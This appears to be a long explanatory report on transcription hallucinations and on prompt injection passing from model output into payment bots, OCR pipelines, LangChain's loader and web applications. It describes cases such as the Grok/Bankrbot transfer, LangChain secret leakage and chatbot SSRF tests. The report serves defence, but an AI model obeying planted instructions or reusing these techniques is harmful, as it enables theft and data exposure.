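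Whisper has its own check for this. It estimates the probability *p* that a segment contains no speech and the average log-probability *l* of the words it has written, which measures its confidence in them. The program discards the segment only if

*p* > τₚ and *l* < τₗ,

where τₚ and τₗ are fixed thresholds. A confident invention therefore gets through however high *p* is. Aparin, Popov and colleagues (2026), in *Whisper Hallucination Detection and Mitigation via Hidden Representation Steering and Sparse AutoEncoders*, found that the two conditions let through 86.88% of their recordings without speech. They reduced this to 27.33% by adjusting the model's internal activity as it ran, with a small loss of accuracy on real speech.

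### Deleting known false phrases

Whisper's hallucinations often repeat the same phrases. In the experiment by Barański and colleagues, "thank you" and "thanks for watching" made up about 35% of all hallucinations, probably because Whisper was trained partly on video subtitles. An ordinary program could therefore search each transcript for known false phrases and delete them.

Their list includes only phrases that Whisper invented more than four times and that people rarely say, meaning that a simple statistical model of English gave them a log-probability below −10. "Thanks for watching" qualified with a score of −13.32. The list omits "Thank you", which scored −9.22, because deleting it everywhere would remove too much real speech. "Thank you" was the most common invention and accounted for a quarter of the total.

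The program first removes loops, in which Whisper repeats the same words over and over, and then deletes the listed phrases. The team tested it on recordings of speech with other sounds added before or after, and compared it with a voice detector that cuts out the parts without speech before transcription. They measured the word error rate,

WER = (S + D + I) / N,

where *S*, *D* and *I* are the numbers of substituted, deleted and inserted words and *N* is the number of words really spoken. Invented words count as insertions, so the rate can exceed 100%.

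| Treatment | WER, sound before or after speech | WER, sound also overlapping speech |
|---|---|---|
| None | 104.8% | 112.0% |
| Loop and phrase removal | 17.1% | 21.1% |
| Voice detector (Silero) | 8.0% | 10.8% |
| Both | 6.5% | 9.4% |

This is a large improvement for a simple filter, but the phrase list may account for only part of it. About 71% of the errors that the team detected in the untreated transcripts involved loops, and they did not test phrase removal separately. They also report that no hallucinations remained after filtering, but they had defined a hallucination as a loop or a listed phrase, and the program deletes both. The voice detector did better on its own, although *Calm-Whisper* (2025) warns that no such detector removes all non-speech.

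Later tests on real speech were less encouraging. *From Text Metrics to Model Internals* (Jasiński, Barański and colleagues, 2026) compared detectors on 3,611 Whisper transcripts of company earnings calls. People had labelled the inventions in them for *HALAS* (2026), a dataset covering seven speech recognisers. Of these transcripts, 23.8% contained an invention. Each detector was scored by how often it ranked a transcript with an invention above one without, so guessing scores 50%. Looking for known phrases scored 53.8%. A detector that read Whisper's internal states scored 85% or more and caught about two-thirds of the inventions. Most of the inventions that every method missed were single words such as "was", which nobody could identify from the text alone.

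Zolkepli concludes that a phrase list works only on audio already known to contain no speech. On recordings without speech, 53.6% of the outputs from one version of Whisper exactly matched a phrase on a list of 40,891. On recordings with speech from the same collection, about 18% to 22% still matched. Some of those matches were probably invented too, since Zolkepli had collected recordings on which a model failed, but others may have been things that people said.

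A filter that ignores this will delete real speech. "Thank you for watching" scored −12.42, so it qualifies for the 2025 list, and a filter that uses plain text search would cut "thank you for watching the children" to "the children". "I'm not sure what I'm doing here" also qualifies, and it may be the most important sentence in a recording of a confused patient. The 2025 test was unlikely to reveal this problem because it used 80 short recordings from a public collection of people reading sentences aloud, and such recordings are unlikely to contain these phrases.

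Barański and colleagues suggest tailoring the list to the setting. A hospital could safely delete a subtitler's credit, for example, because no doctor would say it. They also suggest checking each match against the audio with forced alignment, which estimates when each sound in the phrase would have occurred. Sounds that fit the audio poorly or have implausible lengths suggest that the model invented the phrase. The safest program would keep all the text, mark a matched phrase as doubtful if the voice detector found no speech at that point, and leave the decision to someone who can listen to the audio.

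Retraining the recogniser to stay silent can also make it miss real speech. Zolkepli tested a Malaysian version of Whisper that its developers had trained on recordings without speech. It produced words for only 9.3% of non-speech sounds, compared with 89.9% for Whisper large-v3, but it recovered only 41.1% of spoken phrases, compared with 69.8%. Zolkepli then trained Whisper on silence together with synthetic recordings of the phrases it commonly invents. The best version recovered 82.7% of spoken phrases and produced words for 2.4% of silent clips, down from 61.9%, but its accuracy across 58 languages fell.

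### Instructions on the page

Scanned letters and forms go through a similar pipeline, with optical character recognition (OCR) in place of speech recognition. Traditional OCR software identifies characters by shape. Many developers now use a vision-language model, which takes a picture of the page and writes out the text. Because the model can follow instructions, it may obey a sentence on the page instead of copying it. When Mistral released such a product in March 2025, Willison called this the big question about using language models for OCR, in *mistral ocr*. A Mistral employee replied that the product "should be robust".

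Liu, Xu and colleagues (2026), in *What Survives the Shift from Text to Pixels?*, tested other models by asking them to copy a hostile passage word for word without carrying it out. On page images, Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite copied the passage correctly in 91% to 98% of cases, depending on what the passage demanded. Qwen3-VL-8B, a small open model, did so in 67% to 76%, and GPT-5-nano in 37% to 54%. Some of these failures were misreadings rather than obedience. Obedience was much clearer when Qwen received the document as text. When asked to copy an instruction to replace the answer with a set phrase, it wrote the set phrase in 89 of 90 cases.

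Transcribing a page can also make the next model more likely to follow an instruction on it. Liu and colleagues had Qwen answer questions about documents containing an instruction to add a marker to the answer or change its format. Qwen followed the instruction in 1.11% of cases when given the page as an image, and in 41.80% when given an OCR transcript of the same page, despite the recognition errors. A museum that scans a letter and passes the text to a summarising model may therefore be more exposed to instructions in the letter than one that gives the model the scan.

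But keeping the page as an image is not a dependable defence. Qwen followed an instruction to replace its whole answer on 77.96% of page images, and larger type or a sharper image made it more likely to do so. When the researchers tried up to eight wordings of each instruction, images lost most of their advantage for Qwen.

Vision-language models also correct text they should copy. Lee, Ak and colleagues (2026), in *Do VLMs Read or Rewrite?*, altered about 5% of the characters on printed pages and asked 15 systems to transcribe them. Many models transcribed "prbolem" as "problem". Traditional OCR restored none of the scrambled English words to their original spelling, while Qwen3.5-4B restored 27.35% and olmOCR-2-7B, a model specialised for OCR, restored 58.63%. Gemini-3-Flash also restored none, so not all vision-language models have this fault. Altered words also increased errors in the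 rest of the page, by as much as 7.3 times for one model. Correcting a typing error is usually helpful, but an odd spelling in a contract or a medical record may be a surname or evidence of forgery.

### Checking the text against the source

The simplest safeguard is to keep the recording or scan next to the text, along with the raw transcript and the model's draft. A reader who doubts a sentence can then check it against the original, and comparing the versions shows which step introduced the error. In Heber City, the film's lines would have been in both the raw transcript and the recording. But this catches only errors that somebody suspects. Invented sentences are fluent, and people use these systems to avoid listening to everything again. Keel told FOX 13 News that he saves six to eight hours a week, and he would lose much of that if he replayed every recording.

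Linking each sentence to a time in the recording makes checking quicker, because the reader can click on a sentence and hear a few seconds of audio. In a demonstration for FOX 13 News, Code Four produced a report with timestamps from a mock traffic stop. The timestamps should come from the speech recogniser, and ordinary code should carry them through. For example, the code can number each segment of the transcript and require the summarising model to cite a number for every sentence. It can then reject a sentence that cites a missing segment, and flag one that cites a stretch where the voice detector found no speech.

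A valid link shows where to listen, but it doesn't prove that the audio supports the sentence. The frog sentence could have had a valid link to the moment when the film's characters were speaking. If the model leaves a sentence out, there is no link to click, but the code can list stretches of speech that no sentence cites. For scanned documents, the equivalent of a link is a box drawn around the source of each passage. *GutenOCR* (2026) describes a model that returns text with such boxes, but *ParseBench* (2026) notes that connecting text to its place on the page is still a weak point for most vision-language models.

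A program can also make two transcripts and hold the message for a person to review if the transcripts differ. Koenecke and colleagues found invented text by running Whisper twice and looking for extra text that changed between runs. They point out that this misses invented text that is the same in both runs, as the stock phrases are likely to be.

A different recogniser is better for checking a transcript. Researchers tested rival services from five companies on 187 clips where Whisper had invented text, and none of them invented any. This evidence is limited because the clips were chosen for Whisper's failures, and each rival might fail on others. In *Whisper-Aware LLM* (2026), three newer recognisers wrote text for 25% to 29% of files containing only noise. If two recognisers each did so on 25% of files, and their errors were unrelated, both would write text for about 6% of the files,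 and their wording would usually differ.

The recognisers' errors may well be related, though. Zolkepli points out that developers trained several popular ones, including NVIDIA's Canary and Parakeet, on transcripts that Whisper had written, and argues that these models inherit Whisper's habits even when the developers filter out the false phrases first. For printed pages, traditional OCR is a more independent check. It can't follow an instruction and didn't restore any of the scrambled words, so comparing its output with a vision-language model's should show where the model followed an instruction on the page or silently corrected the text.

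Comparing transcripts would not have caught the frog error, because two good recognisers would both have transcribed the film's audio. It would also miss a lie or an injected instruction that a caller speaks clearly.

### Marking speech as data

The remaining safeguard is to tell the next model that the transcript is material to work on, not a source of instructions. Liu and colleagues did this throughout their experiment by describing the document as untrusted in the system prompt and marking where it began and ended. The table shows how often each model still obeyed an instruction in a document supplied as text.

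| Model | Add a line | Change the format | Replace the answer |
|---|---|---|---|
| Qwen3-VL-8B | 74% | 72% | 99% |
| GPT-5-nano | 78% | 72% | 30% |
| Haiku 5.5 | 2% | 5% | 1% |
| Gemini 3.1 Flash-Lite | 94% | 98% | 31% |
| GLM-5.3-Flash | 65% | 62% | 0% |
| DeepSeek V4.1 Flash | 65% | 89% | 4% |

The label was not enough for five of the six models. Haiku 5.5 almost always kept to the user's request, but the experiment doesn't show how much of that was due to the label, since there was no unlabelled version for comparison. These are mostly small, cheap models that a transcription service might choose for routine clean-up. A developer would have to test the specific model they use.

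Marking speech as speech can also help the human reader, if the mark stays in the finished record. The museum's template can put "The caller said:" above the message, so that the reader can tell that a false claim about a painting came from the caller. A police template could require the model to attribute every statement it takes from the audio to a speaker or an unidentified voice. The Heber City report might then have recorded, accurately, that a voice in the background said something about a frog.

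## Grok and Bankrbot: a decoded message taken as a payment order

On 4 May 2026, someone asked the chatbot Grok to translate a message from Morse code, and the payment program Bankrbot treated the translation as an order to send about $170,000 in cryptocurrency. Grok belongs to Elon Musk's company xAI and replies publicly to people who tag it on the social network X. Bankrbot, the account of a service called Bankr, carries out financial requests that people post on X, such as buying a cryptocurrency or sending some to a friend. Traders call units of a cryptocurrency tokens, but these are unrelated to the tokens a language model reads.

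Bankrbot worked much like the museum's imaginary refund program, which paid out whenever a post on the staff channel had a certain form. But Bankrbot paid out real money, on a network where anyone can post.

### How Grok came to have a wallet

In a statement quoted in BeInCrypto's *How AI Was Tricked Into Stealing $150,000 From Grok Wallet*, Bankr said it automatically creates a wallet for every X account that interacts with it, and that "whoever controls that account controls the wallet". Grok therefore got a wallet without anyone at xAI needing to open one.

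Grok's wallet dates from March 2025. According to The Block's *Bankrbot ends Grok's unintentional token creation spree by disabling interactions on X* (2025), a user asked Grok to name a new token for Bankrbot to create. Grok suggested DebtReliefBot (DRB), and Bankrbot issued it. At the time, an account had to hold 5 million of Bankr's own tokens to launch a new one. Grok's wallet held too few, so someone from the Bankrbot community sent it the rest. Users then got Grok to launch 16 more tokens, and a share of the trading fees went to its wallet.

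*The Bankr $DRB Surge* (Peaster, 2025) recounts that on 7 March, the day DRB launched, a user persuaded Grok to hand over about 4 ether in fees. BlockTempo (2025) reproduces a post in which Bankr's founder, 0xDeployer, explained that anyone could claim the fees on Grok's behalf. Someone claimed them, which moved them into Grok's wallet, and Grok was then "tricked into sending" them on. 0xDeployer announced that Bankr would stop responding to Grok. The wallet kept collecting fees, and Peaster reports that it took in more than $600,000 between the theft and 14 March.

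The OECD's *Grok AI Breaks Free, Creates Crypto Tokens, Bankrbot Disables Interactions* (2025), an entry in its AI incident monitor, found no evidence of direct or indirect harm in this episode. That finding understated the harm, because the 4 ether was already gone.

### The transfer of 4 May 2026

The larger theft began when the attacker sent Grok's wallet a Bankr Club Membership token, a digital certificate that reportedly unlocked the wallet's full transfer rights. Rivera Campos (2026), in *How Grok got prompt-injected*, writes that the token removed the standard limits on transfers. CryptoSlate's *Grok’s crypto wallet was just exploited by a tweet* treats the membership as only part of the explanation. The wallet had sent away 4 ether in 2025, before Bankr launched the membership scheme, so if the token was necessary in 2026, Bankr must have tightened its rules in between.

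The attacker then posted the Morse code on X. Grok decoded it and replied in plain English, tagging Bankrbot with a request to send 3 billion DRB to a particular wallet. Bankrbot made the transfer on Base, the blockchain network it uses. The attacker moved the tokens to another wallet and quickly sold them. The attacker's X profile disappeared within minutes.

The original post was deleted, so its exact wording is uncertain. CryptoSlate mentions possible formatting tricks in addition to the Morse code. According to the AI Incident Database's *Incident 1556*, the attacker asked Grok to relay the message to Bankrbot as well as translate it. Either way, Grok did roughly what the stranger asked, and its translation may have been accurate.

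Estimates of the tokens' value range from about $150,000 to $200,000. The security firm SlowMist put it at $174,570, according to BitcoinWorld's *SlowMist Reports $174K AI Agent Exploit on Base Chain*. 0xDeployer said 80% of the funds had come back and the DRB community would discuss the rest, which would be about $35,000 at SlowMist's valuation. A group called the DRB Task Force objected to this account. According to BeInCrypto, it said the attacker offered to return the 80% only after the community had obtained his personal details, and it called the episode outright theft. Bankr couldn't simply reverse the payment, so recovery depended on identifying the attacker and getting him to cooperate.

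### How much of Bankrbot was a model

Bankrbot apparently used a language model to read posts too, so it wasn't purely a relay program. Bankr advertises trading "through natural language", and 0xDeployer described the old block on Grok as a defence against one language model injecting instructions into another.

Bankr also used ordinary code around that model. 0xDeployer said the block on Grok was hardcoded. Bankr's technical documentation from later in May describes code that removes the transfer tools from an agent's session if the user has chosen read-only access, and code that checks each transaction just before sending it to the blockchain. These statements don't show how the model interpreted Grok's reply, or how the work was divided between the model and the code on 4 May.

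Privy's *Bankr Twitter bot guide* shows how such a bot can work. Privy supplies Bankr's wallets, and its guide explains how to build a similar bot, though the sample code isn't Bankr's own. Simplified and put into Python, the payment step looks like this:

```python
order = model(post.text)
wallet = wallets[post.author_id]
wallet.send(order["recipient"], order["amount"])
```

The model turns the post into a structured order with an amount and a recipient. Code then looks up the posting account's wallet and sends the money without asking anyone to confirm. X supplies the author's identity, so the wording of a post can't make the model use a different account's wallet. But if the post comes from Grok's account, the code uses Grok's wallet, regardless of who thought of the payment.

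Privy's sample pays only X accounts tagged in the post. This restriction might have hindered the attacker, since the sample would have rejected an order that gave only a wallet address. An attacker could get around it by having Grok tag an account the attacker owned.

### Who posted and who authorised

Security engineers distinguish *authentication*, which establishes who sent something, from *authorisation*, which establishes whether the sender may take the action and has chosen to. Bankr used authentication for both, so Bankrbot acted on good evidence that Grok's account had posted the order but no evidence that anyone entitled to spend the money wanted to make the payment.

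This usually works for a personal account, because the person with the password also writes the posts. But Grok's account answers almost anyone who tags it, so a stranger could choose much of what it posted even though xAI had the password. Bankr had said that whoever controls the account controls the wallet, and it hadn't intended this to include strangers who could prompt Grok's posts, but in practice it did. Like the compiler in Hardy's story of the confused deputy, Grok had authority that the attacker lacked, and used it at the attacker's request.

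A person could also order a payment by accident, by solving a Morse puzzle in public or quoting someone else's post. Most people would notice that the message was an order to empty their own wallet, but a payment program shouldn't rely on that, because a post can contain an order that its author didn't mean to give.

The membership token involved a similar mistake. Bankr apparently expanded the wallet's rights because the wallet held the token, although the owner hadn't asked for them. In 2025, outsiders had already used a gift to unlock token launches. Bankr could have left any new rights inactive until the owner logged in and accepted them.

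It would also have helped to follow the rule from Willison and Bista's exchange, that a model's privileges should drop to those of whoever wrote the text it is processing. Grok was answering a stranger, so Bankr should have let the reply trigger payments only from the stranger's money. X records which post a reply answers, so Bankr's code could have looked up who had asked. The rule is harder to apply in a long thread, where Grok may draw on posts by several people.

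### Which safeguards would have stopped it

Several safeguards would have blocked the transfer, but some work only if an owner turns them on. 0xDeployer said that no one at xAI administered Grok's wallet, so the default settings mattered more than the optional ones.

| Safeguard | Effect on the transfer of 4 May | Theft still possible |
|---|---|---|
| Ignoring posts by Grok | Stops it | Through any other account that repeats strangers' words |
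| Signed commands on a separate channel | Stops it, if Grok can't sign | If someone steals the key or tricks its holder |
| Limit of $500 per payment and per day | Stops a payment of that size | Up to $500 a day |
| Fixed recipients | Stops it, if someone has set up the list | Through bad trades, or payments to listed recipients |
| Owner's confirmation outside X | Stops it | If the owner approves without checking |

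**Ignoring automated accounts.** Bankr had already blocked its agent from acting on Grok's replies, but 0xDeployer said the team did not carry the block over when it rewrote the agent. An automated test would have exposed the omission before release by posting a small payment order from Grok's account and checking that Bankrbot ignored it. Bankr has since added a stronger block.

Blocking one account doesn't prevent the same problem with another chatbot, and X accounts run by software don't always identify themselves. It would be safer to accept orders only from accounts whose owners had logged in and asked to use posts for payments. Posts from Grok's account then couldn't have moved money from its wallet unless someone at xAI had opted in. Bankr instead added a setting that lets each owner turn off actions triggered by replies on X, which protects only the owners who find it.

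xAI could also have acted on its side by removing Bankrbot's tag from Grok's replies. CryptoSlate suggests checking replies for text that resembles a command, as well as decoding suspicious posts before answering them. Checking the finished reply is more reliable than looking for Morse code, because the attacker could have used another code but Bankrbot still had to receive a readable order. Even so, xAI would have to know about every bot that acts on a tag.

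A payment service can refuse orders from public posts and accept only signed requests sent through a separate channel. Fintoc, a payments company, requires a digital signature on each transfer request, which a program computes from the request using a secret key. The signature includes a timestamp and a number that works only once. Fintoc rejects any request that is unsigned, expired, repeated or altered. Grok's reply had no signature, so under a rule like this Bankrbot would not have treated it as a payment order.

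The signature shows that someone with the key approved the request. If xAI had given Grok a tool for signing payments, the attacker could have asked Grok to use it, and the order would have arrived with a valid signature. The key has to stay with a person, or with a program that doesn't act on strangers' text.

Requiring signatures would cost Bankr some of its appeal, since its main attraction is that people can trade by writing a post. Bankr could keep most of that convenience by letting a post prepare a payment that the owner then approves elsewhere. Its website would be suitable for this, because owners already log in there with their X credentials and Grok can't log in by writing a reply.

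Bankr's *Protecting Your Account* lists default spending limits of $500 for a single transaction and $500 over any 24 hours. According to Bankr's May documentation, changing these limits requires a web login, and the program rejects a payment if it can't find the token's price. It is unclear whether the limits were in force on 4 May. If they had been, the order for 3 billion DRB would have failed.

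The attacker could then have asked for smaller payments. At SlowMist's valuation, taking all the tokens at $500 a day would have required 350 daily payments, and somebody would probably have noticed well before the end. A limit therefore reduces the loss and gives people time to notice, but it does not settle who authorised the payment. It must also stay in place when someone sends the wallet a gift. If the membership token really did lift the wallet's earlier limits, anyone with a membership to give away could have removed them.

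Bankrbot let a stranger's text set all 160 bits of the recipient's address on Base. If the owner lists ten permitted recipients in advance, the text can only determine which of the ten is paid, which takes at most log₂(10), or about 3.3 bits. The attacker's address wouldn't have been on the list. Bankr now offers such a list, with a default delay of 24 hours before a new entry takes effect, so even someone who gets into the owner's account can't add an address and use it immediately. But the list is off by default, and an unattended wallet probably wouldn't have had one.

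A list of allowed recipients may also fail to prevent harmful trades. Bankr always allows the owner's own addresses, so a stranger might still be able to make the wallet spend its money on a worthless token that the stranger was selling, because the token would be delivered to the owner.

Asking a wallet's owner to confirm a payment works only if the request goes somewhere the attacker can't answer it. If Bankrbot had replied on X to ask whether Grok was sure, the attacker could have prompted Grok to say yes. If it had asked through Bankr's website and nobody at xAI was managing the wallet, the request would have gone unanswered, and a program that treats silence as a refusal would not have paid.

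Banks already combine language models with this kind of check. *Banking Done Right* describes Ryt AI, a banking assistant in which models interpret customers' requests, with fixed rules and human confirmation as safeguards. The confirmation screen should take the amount and recipient directly from the transaction the program is about to send. If a model writes the description instead, an injection could make a payment to a stranger look like one to a friend.

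The other controls that Bankr promoted after the theft would have done little to stop this attack. They included restrictions on API keys, which other software uses to connect to Bankr, and on the internet addresses it can connect from. These help protect against a stolen key, but the attacker didn't need one because the order arrived as a public post from a genuine account.

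## LangChain and web applications: model text read as code

Bankrbot took its order in plain English. Most receivers instead rely on *control markers*, character sequences that a program reads as structure or commands rather than content. In a web page, an angle bracket followed by a letter starts a tag. In a database query, an apostrophe can end a piece of text. Ordinary writing contains the same characters, so a relay program needs an escaping rule to mark them as content. Without one, whoever wrote the text can add their own structure.

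### A reserved key in LangChain

LangChain is a library for building applications on language models, with about 98 million downloads a month in late 2025. Its applications often save their objects, such as the messages in a conversation, and load them again later. LangChain writes each object as a JSON dictionary, a set of named entries, and marks it with the reserved key `lc`:

```json
{
  "lc": 1,
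  "type": "constructor",
  "id": ["langchain_core", "messages", "ai", "AIMessage"],
  "kwargs": {"content": "The museum opens at ten."}
}
```

When the loader finds this marker, it builds the type of object named in `id`, using the settings in `kwargs`. If a dictionary has no marker, the loader returns it as plain data.

GitHub's advisory for CVE-2025-68664, *GHSA-C67J-W6G6-Q2CM* (2025), traces the flaw to LangChain's saving functions, which did not escape ordinary dictionaries containing an `lc` key. If an attacker got such a dictionary into the data, LangChain saved it unchanged, and the loader then treated it as one of LangChain's own objects.

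The dictionary could come from a model, because replies in LangChain carry extra fields of structured data alongside the text, and the advisory warns that prompt injection can control those fields. Some streaming and chat-history features save and reload them automatically, so a developer could be exposed without calling the loader. The advisory lists twelve affected uses.

A marker written in the text of a reply would have loaded as ordinary text and had no effect, because a JSON encoder puts a backslash before each quotation mark inside a string. LangChain escaped correctly for the JSON parser but not for its own loader, which gives a special meaning to a key that JSON treats like any other.

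The loader could also fetch secrets. Programs often keep passwords and access keys in named settings called environment variables. One type of marked dictionary stood for an environment variable, and by default the loader replaced the dictionary with the variable's value. If the application then showed the loaded data to the attacker, any secret in it leaked.

An attacker could steal a key even without seeing any output, according to Cyata (2025), the security company whose researcher found the flaw. The loader built objects only from approved packages, but these included a connector for Amazon's models that sent a web request as soon as the loader created it. The attacker could choose the address and have the loader put a secret in the request. Cyata's researcher also looked for a way to run arbitrary code and found that the loader could build a template in Jinja2, a format that can execute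 Python. The code would run only if the application later filled in the template.

The flaw remained in a widely studied library for two and a half years. Cyata attributes this to auditors' natural focus on the loading code, where the damage happens, whereas the fault was a missing line in the saving code. GitHub's *GHSA-R399-636X-V7F6* (2025) describes a similar flaw in LangChain's JavaScript version.

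### The fix and its gaps

The corrected library wraps any ordinary dictionary that contains the reserved key. Suppose the museum's data uses "lc" to mean the lower corridor:

```text
Original:  {"lc": "closed for repairs"}
Saved:     {"__lc_escaped__": {"lc": "closed for repairs"}}
```

The loader removes the wrapper and returns the contents as data, without building anything. The wrapper is a new control marker, so it needs escaping too. LangChain also wraps a dictionary whose only key is `__lc_escaped__`, according to the copy of its source code on Supermodel, a software documentation site. Otherwise the loader would strip a wrapper that belonged to the user's own data.

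LangChain changed the loader's defaults at the same time, so it now builds only classes from the core package, doesn't read secrets from environment variables, and refuses Jinja2 templates. Escaping should make these limits unnecessary, but they reduce the damage if the escaping fails again.

In May 2026, GitHub's *GHSA-PJWX-R37V-7724* (2026) reported another failure, in which a mistake in the check for secrets let some crafted dictionaries avoid the wrapper. Several older features also called the loader with its widest list of permitted classes, which overrode the stricter default. LangChain corrected the check and deprecated three of those features, meaning that developers should stop using them.

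LangChain's advice has also become stricter. In an older copy of its reference page *load*, LangChain calls the default list safe for simple types such as messages and documents. In a newer copy, it calls the default unsafe for untrusted data and recommends permitting only message classes. It points out that a saved object can carry settings, including the web address that a model connector will contact.

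"Safe" here means that building a message triggers no further action. The attacker can still forge a message that seems to come from the assistant, and the May advisory warns that the forged message could stay in the chat history and influence later replies. It is safer to reduce untrusted input to plain text before LangChain receives it. According to the same advisory, applications that do this are unlikely to be exposed, because they leave no dictionary for the loader to misread.

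### Templates

LangChain had a related flaw, CVE-2025-65106, in its prompt templates. A developer might write the template `User question: {question}`, where the braces mark a gap to fill. Braces in the user's question cause no trouble, because Python doesn't search the inserted text for more gaps.

The template is dangerous when an outsider writes it. OSV's *PYSEC-2026-1518* (2026), an entry in a public database of software flaws, explains that a placeholder could name an object's internal attributes as well as a variable. Starting from a chat message, an attacker might follow those attributes to the application's environment variables. LangChain's fix allows only simple variable names in these templates. GitHub's *GHSA-926X-3R5X-GFHW* (2026) reported the following April that the fix was incomplete, because two kinds of template skipped the check and the check missed placeholders nested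 inside formatting instructions.

A relay program creates the same danger if it uses a model's reply as a template. *From Prompt Injection to Web Exploitation* (Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian, 2026) describes an application that used the reply as a Jinja2 template, which allowed a prompt to make the server run an operating-system command. The application should have inserted the reply as a value into a template written in advance. Build jobs that paste outside text into shell scripts make a similar mistake.

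### One string, three receivers

Suppose a model summarises an enquiry to the museum about a framed picture as follows:

```text
O'Hara <oak frame, 12">
```

The relay program has to show this text on a web page, store it in a database and send it to another program as JSON. Pasting in the raw text would fail in all three places. A browser would read everything from the first angle bracket to the last as an unknown tag and display only "O'Hara". A database would treat the apostrophe as the end of the text and reject what followed. A JSON parser would stop at the inch mark.

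Standard Python functions handle all three:

```python
page = "<p>" + html.escape(text) + "</p>"

db.execute("INSERT INTO enquiries (summary) VALUES (?)", (text,))

message = json.dumps(text)
```

| Receiver | What the program sends for the summary |
|---|---|
| Web page | `O&#x27;Hara &lt;oak frame, 12&quot;&gt;` |
| Database | `O'Hara <oak frame, 12">` |
| JSON parser | `"O'Hara <oak frame, 12\">"` |

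The browser turns each code back into its character, and the JSON parser removes the outer quotation marks and the backslash. The database gets the original text because this is a *parameterised query*, in which the question mark reserves a place for the value. The program passes the value separately, so it needs no escaping. OWASP's *SQL Injection Prevention Cheat Sheet* strongly discourages escaping text by hand and pasting it into the query, because escaping rules differ between databases and are easy to get wrong.

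No single clean-up function can replace these three lines, because a function returns one result for each input and the receivers need three different results. If the program HTML-encoded everything, the database would store `O&#x27;Hara`, and a search for O'Hara would find nothing. The web page would then encode the text again, and visitors would see the codes instead of the punctuation.

Deleting every suspicious character would misspell the name and lose the measurement. It also wouldn't make the text safe for every receiver, because LangChain's marker was a key made of two ordinary letters and Bankrbot acted on a sentence.

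Even a single browser applies different rules to different parts of a page. OWASP's *Cross Site Scripting Prevention Cheat Sheet* explains that HTML encoding works for text between tags but not for JavaScript in an event handler, the part of a tag that runs when, for example, someone clicks. The browser decodes the HTML before it runs the JavaScript. The JSON version leaves angle brackets unchanged, so a server that mislabels its JSON as a web page can make the browser look for tags in it.

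OWASP therefore recommends encoding text as close as possible to the point of display, where it is clear which rules apply. When a filter runs on incoming text, it isn't yet clear where that text will end up. The museum should store the original summary and encode a copy each time it builds a page.

Filtering the input is even weaker when a language model is involved, because the model can create markers that weren't in the input. Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe a 2024 demonstration on DeepSeek's chat site. The prompt contained a script disguised in Base64, an encoding that uses letters, digits and a few symbols, and an instruction to decode it. The site put the decoded reply straight into the page, where the script could read the user's login token. A filter that checked the prompt for angle brackets would have found none, just as a filter that checked for payment orders might have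 missed the Morse code sent to Grok. If the site had encoded the reply for HTML, the browser would have displayed the script as harmless text.

### Values and whole commands

OWASP advises developers to use parameterised queries for every database operation that involves model output. This works when the model supplies a value, such as a name to look up, because the programmer has already written the query. The worst outcome is then a lookup of the wrong name.

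In another case that Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian describe, a shop's chatbot looked up any order number a customer gave it without checking who had placed the order. The numbers followed a predictable pattern, so a stranger could collect other customers' email and delivery addresses. A parameterised query would not have prevented this, because each order number was a legitimate value. The program should also have required the order to belong to the logged-in customer, and taken that customer's identity from the login session instead of from the model.

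Some parts of a query can't be parameters, including the names of tables and columns and the direction of sorting. The programmer can let the model choose these from a list:

```python
COLUMNS = {"date": "received_at", "name": "sender_name"}
ORDERS = {"ascending": "ASC", "descending": "DESC"}

column = COLUMNS[choice["sort_by"]]
order = ORDERS[choice["direction"]]

db.execute(
    "SELECT summary FROM enquiries WHERE sender_name = ? "
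    f"ORDER BY {column} {order}",
    (choice["sender"],),
)
```

The model picks a label, and the code supplies the SQL. A label that isn't on the list raises an error before the query reaches the database. The sender's name is still free text, and the code passes it to the query as a parameter.

Parameters don't protect the database when the model writes the whole query. Some chatbots turn a question in English into SQL and run the result. If a stranger asks for everything in the users table, the model can write a valid query that returns it. The database can't separate the stranger's part from the programmer's, because the model wrote all of it. Checking for stray quotation marks won't help either, since every character is supposed to be code.

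The program has to limit what a query can do. It can parse the model's SQL and accept only queries that fit a *restricted grammar*, for example a single SELECT statement that reads certain columns of one table. Checking the SQL for forbidden words such as DELETE is less reliable, because it would block a harmless query that searches for that word and let through a query that reads the wrong table.

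The database can also enforce limits. OWASP recommends giving each application an account with only the rights it needs, and using a *view*, a virtual table that exposes selected data. The museum's chatbot might have read-only access to a view that contains the date and subject of each enquiry but no names or phone numbers. Even a query that got past the parser then couldn't return a phone number or delete a record. A very slow query could still tie up the database, so the museum would also need a time limit on queries.

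Web addresses raise the same problem when the model supplies the entire address, because its text then determines which computer the server contacts. Attackers use this to reach private services that trust the server, an attack called *server-side request forgery*. If the model instead supplies only an event name, which the code puts into a fixed address, the program can check the name against a list.

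### Tests with a ticket assistant

Tsigkopoulos and Ntantogian tested this attack in April 2026 on TicketOracle, a web application they built for the purpose. Its chatbot answers questions about concerts and has one tool, which fetches any web address the model gives it. The same machine runs an administrative service that can list and delete users. Outsiders can't connect to that service, but the chatbot can.

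In four direct attacks, the attacker typed instructions into the chat to find out which of the machine's ports (numbered connection points) were in use, read users' records, delete data, and delete data through an address that returned an empty response. The table shows how many of ten attempts succeeded with no restrictions on addresses.

| Model | Probe ports | Read records | Delete data | Delete, empty response |
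|---|---|---|---|---|
| Llama 3.3 70B | 10 | 10 | 10 | 10 |
| Qwen3 Coder 480B | 9 | 10 | 10 | 7 |
| DeepSeek R1 | 10 | 10 | 10 | 7 |
| GPT-oss 120B | 3 | 0 | 10 | 0 |
| Gemini 3 Pro Preview | 0 | 7 | 10 | 0 |
| GPT-5.2 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |
| Claude Opus 4.6 | 0 | 0 | 0 | 0 |

The application was equally open to attack in every row, so the differences come from the models. The first three columns may understate the danger, because an attempt counted as a success only if the chatbot also reported the result. A chatbot that deleted a user without saying so would have scored zero. For the fourth attack, the researchers checked the server's log instead.

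The first defence tested was a stricter system prompt that listed the permitted address patterns and event names and instructed the model to refuse everything else. With this prompt, none of the direct attacks succeeded on any model.

In the indirect attack, the attacker posted a concert review containing an instruction. When an innocent user later asked what people thought of the concert, the chatbot fetched the review. Under the original prompt, the attack succeeded six times out of ten on Llama, five on GPT-oss, and never on the other five models. Under the stricter prompt, successes rose to ten out of ten on Llama and fell to zero on GPT-oss.

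The researchers conclude that the rules amplified the attack on Llama, but the experiment can't establish this because they also changed the attack. When they tested the stricter prompt, the planted review included a false claim that the administrative address had been added to the list of permitted addresses, which may account for the extra successes. The ten attempts also took place in a single conversation, so an early success or refusal could have influenced later attempts. Claude Opus 4.6's refusals, for example, went from long explanations to almost single words.

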